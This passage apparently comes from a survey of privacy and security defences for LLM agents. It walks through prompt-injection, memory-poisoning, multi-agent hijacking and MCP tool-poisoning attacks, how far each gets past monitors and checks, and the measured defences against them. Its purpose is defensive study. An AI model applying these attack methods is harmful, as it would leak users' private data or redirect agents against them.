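The AgentCIBench range covers only agents that completed more than 75% of tasks. Among these, Claude Opus 4.7 had the lowest leakage rate and Gemini 3.1 Pro the highest, so an agent's ability to finish tasks says little about how well it protects private information. Excluding refusals matters because GPT-5.4 kept its overall leakage fairly low mainly by refusing tasks. On AgentCIScope, Claude Opus 5 with Claude Code leaked least and Gemini 3.8 Flash with Google's agent software leaked most.

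Models often violate privacy norms that they can recognise when asked. In *MPCI-Bench* (2026), which tests agents that handle images, Qwen3-VL-30B did well at recognising privacy norms but leaked images in over 90% of the cases where sharing was inappropriate. Adding a privacy instruction to the prompt does not close this gap. Staab and colleagues found that such an instruction changed the share of steps without a leak by at most 3.2 percentage points, and sometimes reduced it.

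### Giving the agent only the data its task needs

An agent cannot disclose a medication it has never received. Bagdasarian, Kairouz and colleagues (2024), in *AirGapAgent*, use one model to select the data for a task and a second model to talk to the third party. The first model, the minimiser M, receives the user's task t, their profile U and a general privacy instruction d. It returns the part of the profile that the task needs:

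U_min = M_d(t, U)

For a restaurant booking, U_min might contain the user's name and phone number. The second model receives only U_min, so it cannot reveal the user's medication even if asked. The third party's messages never reach the minimiser. If a doctor asks for something the minimiser left out, the agent can ask the user to release it. AirGapAgent withholds the user's own data, unlike the context minimisation described earlier, which removes untrusted text to defend against injection.

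The threat model includes third parties that simply ask for more than they need and those that invent circumstances to justify their request. Bagdasarian and colleagues tested both on eight tasks, including the doctor's appointment and the job interview, using 20 synthetic profiles of 26 fields each. Utility is the share of appropriate information the agent provided, and privacy is the share of inappropriate information it withheld. The table shows results for Gemini Ultra on the full set of multiple-choice questions.

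| Third party | Agent | Utility | Privacy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Asks plainly | Full profile | 91.6% | 88.5% |
| Asks plainly | AirGapAgent | 83.9% | 96.8% |
| Invents circumstances | Full profile | 98.0% | 33.1% |
| Invents circumstances | AirGapAgent | 90.3% | 93.2% |

With plain questions, minimisation reduced leakage from 11.5% to 3.2% but also withheld more of the information the task required. Minimisation depends on a precise description of the task. When the minimiser received only a general area, such as health or scheduling, average privacy fell from 96.8% to 68.6%.

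These results come from 2024 models, and Gemini Ultra also produced the labels for which answers were appropriate. It labelled vacation preferences as appropriate for a job interview, on the grounds that an employer has to schedule shifts. The profiles were unusually easy to minimise because each fact had its own field. In a real mailbox, the time of an appointment and the reason for it may be in the same sentence.

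### Tracking protected records through tool calls

An agent that needs the medication for one message could still include it in another. FLOWSEAL, the system in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, therefore lets the agent read sensitive records but checks what it sends. The threat model is an outsider who persuades the agent to share those records through ordinary requests, without an injection. The agent software and its tools are trusted. The same check can also catch accidental disclosures.

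Before the agent starts, the owner or the software registers each sensitive record with its owner and the people who may receive it. An interceptor, ordinary code outside the model, then handles every tool call:

1. When a tool returns data, the interceptor looks for registered records in it and notes which ones the agent has read.
2. If the agent combines several records into a summary, the summary inherits the restrictions of all of them.
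3. When the agent tries to write or share something, the interceptor checks the destination. It allows trusted recipients and blocks those on a blacklist.
4. For any other recipient, a separate model receives only the protected records and the proposed text. It returns SAFE if the text reveals nothing from the records and BLOCKED otherwise.

FLOWSEAL's confidentiality theorem states that nothing derived from a protected record reaches an unauthorised recipient unless the checking model wrongly returns SAFE. The guarantee therefore depends on the model getting the hardest part of the task right, which is recognising when a text reveals a record in different words. For example, a message that the user cannot drive for a year may reveal their epilepsy without mentioning it.

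The main test used 105 scenarios, each run three times. In one, a man's former wife asks an agent that knows his diagnosis to add its notes to a shared page. A detailed prompt, used as a defence, told the agent to get consent before answering requests for information, but the agent treated her request as ordinary collaboration. Across the scenarios, agents given this type of request leaked 52.2% of the sensitive items under the prompt defence and 0.5% under FLOWSEAL.

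FLOWSEAL completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 44.7% for the same prompt defence and 75.9% for the most useful of the five alternatives. But none of these tasks required protected information. A separate test used records that the recipient legitimately needed and the owner would have agreed to share. FLOWSEAL delivered only 32.7% of these records, while four prompt-based defences delivered 61.0% to 85.6%. The agent often failed to ask for consent, so a doctor's office might never receive the medication records it needed.

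The checking model accounts for much of the system's usefulness. Replacing it with a rule that blocked every unknown recipient kept leakage low, at 1.3%, but the agent completed none of the harmless tasks. A rule that accepted every unknown recipient restored utility to 79.4% but raised leakage to 24.9%.

### Moving the rule into the database

Some privacy rules concern how a result was calculated, which can't be checked from the outgoing text alone. For example, a clinic might let an agent publish statistics only if each figure draws on at least three patients. The agent is allowed to read every record, and a published average doesn't show how many patients it covers.

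Summers, Mohammed and Wu (2026), in *Please Don't Kill My Vibe*, propose Data Flow Control, which enforces such rules inside the database. Its threat model needs no attacker, only an agent that writes a valid query with a result it should not release. In the notation that Summers and Wu later developed, the clinic's rule could be:

```
SOURCE Patients
CONSTRAINT COUNT(DISTINCT Patients.id) >= 3
ON FAIL REMOVE
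```

If the agent asks for the average age of patients on each medication, software called Passant rewrites the query before the database runs it. The rewritten query has the same effect as this one:

```
SELECT medication, AVG(age)
FROM Patients
GROUP BY medication
HAVING COUNT(DISTINCT id) >= 3
```

The last line removes any medication that only one or two patients take. The agent cannot leave this line out, because Passant adds it after the agent writes its query.

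More complex rules need to know which input rows contributed to each output row, known as its provenance. The database can record this in different ways depending on how it runs the query. If row t₁ joins with rows s₁ and s₂, the provenance can be

t₁·s₁ + t₁·s₂ or t₁·(s₁ + s₂)

The first form mentions four rows and the second mentions three, although the result is the same. A rule that counted these mentions could give different answers for the same query, so Summers and Wu apply every rule to the expanded form on the left. Recording all provenance can make a query up to 10,000 times slower, so Passant calculates only the totals that the rules need. This added almost no time on average across five database systems. The tests used rules that removed nothing, so they measured speed but not leakage or utility.

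Some legal duties can be written as such rules. The US Every Student Succeeds Act requires schools to report results separately for groups such as ethnicities. Summers, Mohammed and Wu express this requirement as `COUNT(DISTINCT ethnicity) = 1` for each row. They also cite a US statistical standard that requires at least three people behind each public figure. If a school has only two pupils from some ethnic group, no figure about them can satisfy both rules, so the database has to withhold their results.

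Article 5(1)(c) of the EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) requires data minimisation. Summers, Mohammed and Wu interpret it as forbidding the release of individual records when statistics would be enough. A database can enforce a statistics-only rule, but someone has to decide when statistics are enough for the purpose.

*Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026) extends Data Flow Control to agents by treating each tool call as an attempt to insert a row into a table. In one failure it describes, a user asks for Joyce's health records and the agent, unable to find them, returns Jake's. The paper's rule blocks the answer if it contains a social security number from the agent's records that does not belong to the requested patient. As printed, the rule looks for an exact copy of the number, so it would miss a number with different spacing, or an answer that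 gave Jake's diagnosis without his number.

On AgentLeak, the benchmark this example comes from, rules of this kind reduced the leakage rate by an average of 66.9 percentage points across five open-weight models. AgentLeak does not measure task completion. On AgentDyn, which does, stopping the agent at its first violation reduced task success by 36.2 points in a test with injections. When the software instead reported which rule had failed and where to find permitted data, task success was 6.5 points higher than with the unprotected agent. A language model wrote most of the rules and people checked them, but some were still too strict.

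### Measuring how much an agent leaks

A yes-or-no measure counts a message that reveals one private detail the same as a message that reveals ten. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* therefore reports both the share of runs with any leak and the share of sensitive items that leaked.

Suppose two agents each complete four runs, with four sensitive items per run. The first reveals one item in every run, and the second reveals all four in a single run. Both leak 4 of 16 items, or 25%, but the first leaks in 100% of runs and the second in 25%. An operator who must report every incident would prefer the second agent, while one worried about a full profile reaching a stranger might prefer the first.

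In the experiments, requests disguised as collaboration usually revealed nearly everything when they succeeded. Against one prompt defence, 32.9% of runs had a leak and 31.8% of items leaked. Leaks from an older attack that used a forged consent message were less complete, with a leak in 4.4% of runs and 3.4% of items leaked.

Neither measure accounts for the harm a detail could do. Revealing a favourite restaurant and revealing an epilepsy diagnosis each count as one leaked item. Staab and colleagues also point out that an agent can omit a fact but disclose enough for the recipient to deduce it, so counting copied items can underestimate the leak.

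### Harmless releases that add up

Suppose a clinic's agent reports that a team of five took 30 sick days this year. One person then transfers to another team, and the agent reports that the remaining four took 12 days over the same period. Anyone who receives both reports can calculate that the person who left took 18 days:

30 − 12 = 18

Both figures draw on at least three people, so the clinic's rule allows them. Summers and Wu's version of Data Flow Control checks each query separately, so it would not detect the problem. FLOWSEAL has a similar gap, because several messages could each contain too little of a record for the checking model to detect. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* does not resolve this case.

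An orchestrator could keep a record of what each recipient has received and check new messages against all of it. That would catch the two reports if they went to the same person, but not if they went to two colleagues who later compared them. It also would not cover what a recipient knows from elsewhere, such as an employer's knowledge of why doctors tell people not to drive.

PrivacyFlow, the defence by Staab and colleagues, tries to estimate this knowledge. Before the agent acts, a planning stage traces where each piece of data came from and why the task needs it. It then models what the recipient already knows and simulates what they could infer from the message. Depending on the remaining risk, it shares a reduced version, blocks the message or asks the user. PrivacyFlow raised the share of PrivacyBench sequences without a leak by between 22.1 and 55.2 percentage points and kept most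 of the agents' utility. It still relies on a series of judgements by a language model, and the main tests included no attacker.

### Whether a model may judge what is appropriate

Staab and colleagues argue that no predefined rule can cover every combination of context and recipient. Bagdasarian and colleagues likewise expect tables of private fields to fail as the number of contexts grows. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* warns that if a model reads the requester's messages, those messages can keep it from recognising that it is making a privacy decision. AirGapAgent and FLOWSEAL reduce this risk by controlling what the judging model receives. AirGapAgent's minimiser decides before the third party has written anything, and FLOWSEAL's checker never receives the conversation.

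Fixed rules are easiest to write for the data that agents already protect best. On AgentCIScope, agents leaked credit card details in 17.1% of cases and social security numbers in 29.4%, but booking details in 76.5% and personal preferences in 84.7%. A program can recognise a card number by its format, but whether a hotel booking is private depends on who is asking and who else was travelling.

For sensitive records that an operator can identify in advance, a fixed rule could limit who may receive them, and a model could only narrow that limit. The rule might allow an agent to disclose the epilepsy medication to the doctor's office and the pharmacy, while the model decides whether a particular message needs to mention it. If the model shares too much, the information still reaches only those two recipients. FLOWSEAL gives its model more power, because a mistaken SAFE can release a record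 to someone the owner never approved.

A model that can only withhold information will sometimes block a disclosure the user wants, so the user needs a way to override it. Staab and colleagues found that letting PrivacyFlow ask the user can increase the number of authorised tasks it completes, but also gives the user more decisions to make. For the job at the clinic, the agent could ask whether to tell the personnel department about the medication. A general request for permission to share health data with the clinic would not distinguish the personnel department from the rest of the clinic.

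## Carrying policies across sessions, agents and tool servers

Suppose the user allows the clinic's personnel department to know about the medication, and the agent saves a note of this permission in its memory. When the agent reads the note a month later, the text alone does not show whether the user gave the permission or the agent copied it from a stranger's email. The orchestrator may have labeled the source during the original run, but the label is no help later if the orchestrator discards it when the run ends.

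The same information can disappear within a single task. When one agent sends another a report drawn from a web page, the second may have no record of the page and may treat the report as an instruction from its user. The orchestrator also places the descriptions of outside companies' tools in the prompt alongside the operator's own instructions.

### Attacks that wait in memory

*MemoryDojo* (2026), a benchmark for attacks through memory, describes an agent's memory with two operations. After session t, the agent updates its memory M using τ, the record of that session. Before a session, it retrieves the context c that suits the new request x:

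M_t = U(M_{t−1}, τ_t)

c_t = ρ(M_{t−1}, x_t)

The record of a session includes the results of its tool calls, so an injection that has no effect in one session can enter memory and return in a later one. *PerMIT* describes such an attack, Trojan Hippo, in which a single untrusted tool call plants text that becomes active only in a later session. A defence that examines each turn separately cannot connect the tool call to its effect.

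*MemPoison* (2026) tested ten undefended agents. Poisoned memories moved their answers towards the attacker's target in 54.7% to 66.9% of cases, although the same agents were 91% to 97% accurate with clean memories. Agents that stored text as intact records were the most vulnerable, while splitting text into separate facts diluted the malicious content. *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (2026) notes more generally that saving and retrieving more text helps agents with long tasks but also gives attackers more opportunities.

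### Plans and stored results in SPA

In an example from *SPA*, a user asks an agent on Monday to fetch an invoice from Acme and save its details. The invoice contains an attacker's account number and an injected instruction. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay the invoice. In a delayed planning attack, the stored instruction reaches the planner and changes the plan. In a delayed execution attack, the plan is correct, but the agent sends the money to the attacker's stored account number.

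To prevent the first attack, SPA uses plan-then-execute for each request. Its planner writes the plan in a small language with six kinds of step: retrieve a stored result, call a tool, query a quarantined model, display something, choose between branches, and repeat steps for each item in a list.

SPA saves each result as an artefact containing the value, its label and a description. Later planners receive only the description, which gives the artefact's format, what it represents, why the agent produced it and which request it came from. The planner wrote the explanatory parts on Monday before any tool ran, so the invoice's text could not influence them.

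Tuesday's plan might be:

```
retrieve acme_invoice as inv
tool     pay(inv.account, inv.amount)
display  "The invoice has been paid."
```

To prevent the second attack, SPA checks the explicit and implicit flows in the whole plan before running it. Retrieving the invoice restores its untrusted label. If the payment tool requires trusted input, SPA rejects the plan.

SPA would also reject a plan to pay a genuine invoice from Acme, because that invoice came from outside too. Unlike APPA, which offers the agent ways to continue after a refusal, SPA ends the request. The planner receives no explanation and cannot keep submitting revised plans to find one that passes. SPA is more lenient only in what it displays to the user, hiding the forbidden item and showing the rest.

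### Delayed attacks on AgentDojo-MQ

AgentDojo resets the agent after each task, so it cannot measure whether an injection survives from one request to the next. *SPA* introduces AgentDojo-MQ, which divides each of the 97 tasks into a sequence of two to five requests. The researchers mapped by hand which earlier results each step needs, and software split the tasks at those dependencies. GPT-5.4 then wrote the requests, and the researchers reviewed them. The injections are in place from the start of each sequence, and the agent keeps its memory until the end.

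The table shows the results with GPT-5.4 nano. Each configuration faced 949 attacked runs.

| What the planner receives | Flow checks | Utility without attack | Utility under attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Stored values and descriptions | Off | 65.9% | 66.8% | 0.6% |
| Descriptions only | Off | 62.5% | 60.0% | 0.3% |
| Descriptions only | On | 35.3% | 33.7% | 0.2% |
| Descriptions only, real tools hidden | Off | 12.6% | 9.8% | 0.0% |
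| Descriptions only, real tools hidden | On | 9.7% | 8.3% | 0.0% |

The flow checks reduced utility far more than hiding stored values did. They stopped about 45% of runs, mostly because a plan passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted input. The 0.2% attack success rate comes from two runs that AgentDojo counted as successful attacks even though SPA had rejected the plan in both.

The agent could still reuse the hidden values. With the flow checks on, later plans retrieved the right artefact in 89.9% of cases where an earlier request had stored it, or 73.4% when cases where nothing had been stored are included.

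These results provide little evidence about delayed attacks, because even a planner that received every stored value resisted nearly all of them. The injections targeted the current task and rarely affected a later plan, and *SPA* acknowledges that they test delayed poisoning only weakly.

*Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (2026) tests a defence that binds each memory entry to its origin when the agent writes it. The agent cannot send data to an address from an untrusted origin unless a separate step has raised the address's trust level. In the tests, up to eight other sessions passed between planting the attack text and using it. Attacks succeeded 51% to 61% of the time against undefended agents and never against defended ones.

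They also reproduced four published poisoning methods, including Trojan Hippo. None of 1,152 attempts succeeded against the defence, compared with 38.2% against undefended agents. Defended and undefended agents each completed 264 of 384 harmless tasks. A model that judged the content of memories still let through 43.8% of the Trojan Hippo attacks. SPA did reduce utility, probably in part because it has no step that raises trust. Removing that step from this defence made the agent less useful, and SPA's paper suggests adding one to SPA.

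### Hijacking the flow between agents

In many multi-agent systems, a coordinating agent divides a task among sub-agents, such as one that reads files and one that runs code. It chooses which sub-agent to use next based on the sub-agents' reports, including status updates and error messages. *Multi-Agent Systems Execute Arbitrary Malicious Code* (Triedman, Jha and Shmatikov, 2025) showed that an attacker can use these reports to redirect the whole system.

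In attacks by Triedman and colleagues, a file or web page imitated an error message. The sub-agent that read it relayed the message as its own report, and the coordinator responded by having another sub-agent run the attacker's code. The researchers describe the sub-agents as confused deputies because each acted within its permissions. Across five ways of coordinating agents in the AutoGen, CrewAI and MetaGPT frameworks, attacks using a malicious web page succeeded in 45% to 64% of runs on average, compared with at most 1% for earlier prompt injection templates.

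The models were GPT-4o, Gemini 1.5 and smaller versions of each, so these rates do not describe current systems. But an attack could succeed even if one agent resisted it. In one run, a coding agent refused to produce malicious code, but a file-reading agent wrote some instead, and a third agent ran it.

### Secure agents that form an insecure system

A fixed plan for each agent does not solve this problem. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, built a system of three agents and protected each with CaMeL, which writes an agent's whole program before it reads any data. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to go to Julie on Slack. A database agent fetched the records, one of which contained an injection, and the coordinator had a quarantined model summarise them. Neither agent's plan changed. The coordinator then called a notification agent with a line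 like this:

```
notify("Send this summary to Julie on Slack: " + summary)
```

The notification agent treated the whole message as its user's request, so its planner read the injection before writing a plan and added an email that sent the applicants' data to an outside address. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering because untrusted data becomes trusted when it crosses from one agent to another.

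They prove that in any system where agents call other agents as tools, if there are at least two agents and one tool that returns untrusted data, some user request will let that data shape another plan. The proof assumes that users can ask for any tool's result to go into any later call. If the agent with the untrusted tool has a sub-agent, it can build the sub-agent's instructions from the result. If the agent with the untrusted tool is itself a sub-agent, its parent can call it once to get the data and again with instructions based on that data.

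Their remedy, Multi-CaMeL, gives each call two separate inputs:

```
notify(message   = "Send the supplied summary to Julie on Slack",
       variables = {"summary": summary})
```

The receiving planner reads only the message. The interpreter rejects any message that depends on a tool's output, and the variables keep a record of their origin. Every agent's plan therefore depends only on trusted text, so the plans together form one fixed plan for the system. Untrusted data can still affect which branch of that plan runs or introduce false claims into the summary Julie receives.

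To test this, Peters-Gill and colleagues divided AgentDojo's tools among two to four sub-agents and added a coordinator. Across five models, the average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL running separately on each agent, and 0.0% with Multi-CaMeL. All the attacks that succeeded against the separate CaMeL agents used boundary laundering. No attack succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without CaMeL, so most of the evidence comes from older models.

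On AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, protecting each agent separately reduced task success by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and Multi-CaMeL reduced it by another 3.2 points. For the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, the losses were 13.4 and 0.85 points. Some failures occurred without an attacker. When a sub-agent could not find data for the requested machine or dates, it returned data for similar ones, and the coordinator's fixed program continued without adjusting for the substitution.

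The current software also inherits CaMeL's incomplete tracking of implicit flows, so some untrusted values could still reach a message labelled as trusted. Multi-CaMeL's security proof covers only systems where each sub-agent has one parent, so it does not extend to agents that exchange messages freely or share memory.

*SafeFlow* (2026) reconstructs the path untrusted data took between agents and blocks risky actions at the end of that path. Its final rules are deterministic, but language models help reconstruct the path, so decisions can vary between runs. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* includes messages between agents in the same formal model as tool calls, so an access monitor can check both.

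### An authorisation check before execution

Another approach is to assume that some agents will fail and to check the final action they request. Safin, Zisad and colleagues (2026), in *Trust propagation and structural containment in Multi-agent LLM pipelines*, tested this with four components built in LangGraph, a framework for connecting agents. A supervisor, which is ordinary software, calls the other three in a fixed order. The researcher gathers information, the validator reviews the proposed action, and the executor changes a database of email records.

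Before it acts, the executor requires a signed token and approval from a policy oracle. The token is signed with a secret key and is valid for one task and one use. The oracle checks the proposed action and the resources it needs without relying on the validator's result.

The researchers ran 60 tasks, 24 of them unsafe, three times each. In one attack, which they call memory poisoning, a compromised routine replaced the validator and wrote a forged approval into the state the agents share. The routine could also hold the signing key. In the other attack, the researcher agent retrieved a document that falsely claimed the action already had approval.

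Besides counting unsafe actions, Safin and colleagues measured whether the attack had defeated the review. Their judgment bypass rate is

JBR = N_b / N_a

Here N_a is the number of attacked runs with an unsafe task, and N_b is the number of those runs in which the attack skipped or misled the validator.

| Attack | Authorisation checks | Unsafe tasks executed | Safe tasks blocked | Judgment bypass rate |
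|---|---|---|---|---|
| Forged approval in shared state | Off | 100% | 0% | 100% |
| Forged approval in shared state | On | 0% | 0% | 100% |
| False claim in a document | Off | 0% | 59.3% | 0% |
| False claim in a document | On | 0% | 49.1% | 0% |

The second row shows why the separate measure is useful. An operator who counted only unsafe actions would conclude that the system had withstood the attack, although its validator failed every time and only the authorisation checks prevented harm. The attack replaced the validator by design, so the 100% does not estimate how easily a model can be fooled.

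Safin and colleagues then removed the checks one at a time, against an attacker who held the signing key. The system did as well with only the policy oracle as with both checks, but with only the token it did as badly as with neither. A valid signature shows that someone with the key approved the action, but not that the policy allows it. The token could still stop an attacker without the key, which this experiment did not test. The comparison used one set of 60 runs per version.

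The policy in the main test copied the labels that the researchers used to score the tasks, so the result shows that the executor enforced the policy but does not show that the policy could detect new dangers. A second policy, written without those labels, produced the same verdict as the first on all 60 tasks, but the same team wrote it.

The false claim in the document never caused an unsafe action, even without the checks, but it led the validator to block 49.1% of the safe tasks. Adding another model to remove such claims before the review reduced this to 7.4%. The judgment bypass rate rose to 4.2%, or three of 72 runs, but the executor blocked all three actions. The injected claims were conspicuous, and a subtler attack might get past the added model more often.

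### Tool descriptions as instructions

Many agents connect to outside tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP). The user's application opens a session with each tool server and requests a list of its tools. For each tool, the server returns a name, a description in ordinary language and an input format. Agent frameworks copy the description into the model's context to guide when the model uses the tool. MCP doesn't limit the description's length or content.

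A malicious server can put an injection in a tool's description. The agent can read the injection without opening an email or calling the tool, because the description enters the context before the agent starts the user's task. Fixing the plan early therefore does not help if the planner reads the description while writing the plan.

Shaikh and Montaruli (2026), in *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*, connected agents to a malicious server and a legitimate one with tools for files and web requests. They planted a secret in the agent's files and ran 45 attack scenarios with 18 models and 12 configurations (eleven frameworks and OpenAI's interface without a framework). Of the valid runs, 22.9% were vulnerable. In most of these, the agent made a call that carried the attacker's address or read a planted file. They confirmed that the secret reached the attacker's test server in 12.1%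 of the vulnerable runs.

The model mattered much more than the framework. Attack success ranged from 0.4% with Claude Fable 5 to 49.7% with Amazon Nova Pro, while nine of the configurations fell between 23% and 26%. No framework deliberately checked tool descriptions, but Pydantic AI had a lower rate, 16.6%, partly because it rejects duplicate tool names, which blocked scenarios that imitated a legitimate tool. A model that recognises an attack may still carry it out. In four of the ten successful attacks on Claude Sonnet 5, the model wrote that the description contained an injection and then made the harmful call.

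Scanners can look for suspicious tool descriptions before an agent uses them. *MCP-DPT* (2026) surveys several scanners, from simple pattern matching to trained detectors and language models. Shaikh and Montaruli tested a pattern-based scanner, which rejected 20 of the 45 scenarios and wrongly rejected 7.2% of harmless descriptions.

### Pinning definitions and isolating servers

A server can also pass inspection with a harmless tool description and replace it later, which security researchers call a rug pull. Pinning prevents the change from taking effect unnoticed. When the operator approves a tool, the orchestrator stores a cryptographic hash, a short value calculated from the tool's name, description and input format. If the hash of a later listing differs, the orchestrator withholds the tool until someone reviews it. Shaikh and Montaruli found no framework that compared successive descriptions.

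Pinning a tool's description does not protect against one that was malicious from the start. It also does not cover the server's code, so a tool can begin copying its inputs to an attacker while its description stays the same. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) points out that CaMeL, DRIFT and Progent all rely on tools behaving as their interfaces describe. The operator therefore has to limit what each server receives and can do.

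Isolation between servers is one such limit. A poisoned description from a weather service can contain an instruction to send a file using another server's web tool. If a separate agent handles the weather service and has no other tools, it cannot follow that instruction. Its answer still has to return to the main agent as data. Otherwise, the attack crosses the boundary as the applicant's record does in the Multi-CaMeL example.

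*SPA* can also hide real tool descriptions from its planner. One model sees only the user's request and invents the tools needed to fulfill it, and the planner writes a plan with those tools. Another model then reads the real descriptions and matches each invented tool to a real one. A malicious description might still get its tool chosen, but it cannot add a step to the plan. In the tests, about three quarters of runs failed because no match was found.

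SPA labels any value that the planner writes directly into a plan as coming from the user. This is a weakness when SPA shows the planner the real descriptions, because a malicious description could cause the planner to copy an attacker's account number into the plan. The number would then appear trusted and could pass the flow check.

### Authority that shrinks at each hand-over

An agent that hands over part of a task often has more authority than the recipient needs. *Permitted but Unauthorized* (2026) distinguishes what an agent's permissions allow from what another agent has delegated to it. For example, a sub-agent may be asked to read only the Project X emails but have access to the whole mailbox. An ordinary permission check would not stop it from opening a salary letter.

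The paper tested a monitor that keeps a map of which resources each agent has received for its task and blocks access to any others. Without the monitor, three models went outside their delegated tasks in 3, 24 and 27 of 40 runs. None did with it, but the paper notes that this follows from the design, because the monitor blocks exactly what the test counts as a violation. Writing a correct map is harder than enforcing it.

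To keep authority from growing along a chain of agents, the orchestrator can require each delegation to be a subset of the one before. If A₀ is the set of calls the user has authorised, and A₁ and A₂ are the sets passed to the coordinator and then to a sub-agent, the rule is

A₂ ⊆ A₁ ⊆ A₀

Progent applies the same condition when it updates a policy automatically. In the Project X task, the user might authorise the coordinator to read the project emails and send one message to the manager. The coordinator could then allow one sub-agent only to read the emails and another only to send that message. An injection that took over the first sub-agent could not send anything, even if it made that sub-agent ask a third agent for help, because the third agent would receive no more authority than the first sub-agent had.

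A credential, such as a signed token, can carry these limits to a tool server. It would name the task, the permitted calls and an expiry time, and each agent could pass on only a narrower version. Either the server must enforce the limits, or the agent's software must do so before every call. Many servers don't even check who is calling. Shaikh and Montaruli cite a survey of 7,973 remote MCP servers in which 40.55% had no authentication.

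Cancelling the original credential may not be enough after an attack. *SoK* (2026), a survey of multi-agent security, warns that revocation may not recover authority, credentials or derived data that have already spread. If the reader agent has passed a summary to another agent, the orchestrator needs a record of that transfer to remove the summary from the other agent's memory.

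## Rules and architectures in deployed products

A developer who connects an agent to a mailbox may have no labels, no verified monitor and no record of what one agent delegated to another. A simpler precaution is to limit which capabilities the agent has at the same time.

### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, warns against combining three capabilities: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside world. An attacker needs all three to steal data through a prompt injection. Data can leave through a web request, an image or a link as well as through an email tool. Willison addresses the warning to users because no vendor can protect people who combine tools from different suppliers.

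Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) gives developers a similar rule. Within one session, which starts with a fresh context, an agent may have at most two of these properties:

- [A] It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- [B] It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- [C] It can change state or communicate externally.

If a task needs all three properties, the agent should not run autonomously and, at a minimum, needs supervision by a person or another reliable check. Property C is broader than Willison's condition of outside communication because it includes actions that disclose no data, such as deleting a file.

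An agent may sometimes change configuration within a session. In Meta's example, it first browses the web without access to private data, then permanently loses the ability to communicate externally before it opens internal systems. An injection from the web may still be in the context, but the agent can no longer send anything out. If the agent also had tools for changing those internal systems, the orchestrator would have to withdraw those tools too.

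### The email task with one capability removed

The Project X task needs all three properties because the agent reads email that strangers can write, has access to a private mailbox, and sends a message. The table shows how the options Meta gives for an email agent apply to this task.

| Capability removed | How | Cost to the user | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Untrusted content | The agent reads mail only from trusted senders | The summary omits project emails from outside partners | Write from a trusted sender's account, after taking it over |
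| Private data | The agent runs in a test environment without real mail | The agent cannot do the task | Misuse the test environment |
| Free communication | The agent drafts the summary and the user sends it | The user has to review every message | Put false claims in the summary |

Meta also suggests letting the agent send without review to trusted recipients. That suits this task well, since the user named the manager. But the manager may not be entitled to see everything in the mailbox. An injection could make the agent send the manager the user's correspondence with another employer, and a list of trusted recipients would not stop this.

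### Harm that the rules miss

An agent that can read and delete mail but cannot send anything lacks one part of the trifecta, yet an injection could still make it empty the mailbox. The Rule of Two covers this case because the agent reads untrusted text, has access to private mail and can change state.

The Rule of Two is less clear about an agent that moderates a public forum. The agent reads strangers' posts and can delete them, but none of the posts are private. A developer who thinks of property B only as private data would conclude that the agent has only two properties and may run unattended. An injection could then make it delete the whole forum. Meta expects an injection to have no meaningful impact on an agent without property B, but this is true only if the agent can't change anything valuable.

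Neither rule covers mistakes an agent makes without an attacker, such as sending a candidate's background check to a hiring manager. Meta lists agent mistakes and excessive privileges among the problems its rule does not solve. Counting capabilities per session also misses injections stored in long-term memory, unless the developer treats the stored text as untrusted input.

### A browser agent: Gemini in Chrome

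A browser agent often has all three properties, because it reads arbitrary pages while the user is signed in to other sites. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) treats the planning model as inherently vulnerable because it reads untrusted pages. Google trains that model on known attacks, uses spotlighting, and adds the checks in this table.

| What Chrome checks | What decides | Result |
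|---|---|---|
| Whether an action serves the user's goal | A separate model, the User Alignment Critic | The critic approves or vetoes the action |
| Whether a new site is relevant to the task | A variant of the critic | Chrome opens only sites that pass |
| Whether an address written by the model could leak data | A fixed rule | Chrome allows only known, public addresses |
| Whether a page contains an injection | A trained classifier | Chrome prevents actions based on content the classifier flags |
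| Whether a site handles matters such as banking or medical information | A fixed list | Chrome asks the user before the agent goes there |
| Whether the agent needs a saved password | Use of Google's password manager | Chrome asks the user and keeps the password from the model |
| Whether an action is a purchase, payment or message | Partly a classifier | The agent tries to pause for the user |

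The critic receives only metadata about the proposed action, not the unfiltered text of web pages, so a page cannot inject instructions into it directly. When the critic vetoes an action, it gives the planner feedback for another attempt. If attempts keep failing, the planner can return control to the user. An injection may still be in the planner's context during these attempts and can make the planner propose an action that looks compatible with the task.

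The limits on sites extend the same-origin policy, a browser rule that keeps one website's code from reading another's data. The browser identifies each site by its origin, the combination of protocol, host name and port. Without such limits, an agent could read private data on one site and type it into another. *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (2026) tested seven agentic browsers and found that in the least restrictive ones, a malicious site could bypass the policy through a successful injection.

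Google's design has one set of origins the agent may read and another where it may also click and type. Its first version tracked only the second set. In both versions, separating origins would not help much with the Project X task in a webmail site, because the attacker's message, the private mail and the send button all share one origin. The remaining safeguards are the critic, the injection classifier and the confirmation before a message is sent.

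Google's descriptions of that confirmation differ in strength. Parker writes that the agent "will try to pause" before consequential actions. Berschadski (2026) writes in *Future Mode Part 2* that Chrome requires explicit human approval before any high-stakes action. If a classifier decides which actions count as high-stakes, Parker's wording is safer to rely on, because Chrome would not ask the user to approve an action the classifier misses. For companies, Google also applies its data loss prevention rules to agents, so the rules can block transfers of sensitive data by agents as well as employees.

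### An office assistant: Microsoft 365 Copilot

Copilot works with the signed-in user's permissions. Microsoft presents this as a way to contain an attack, since an injection cannot reach data the user cannot open. An executive, however, may be able to open much of the company's confidential material.

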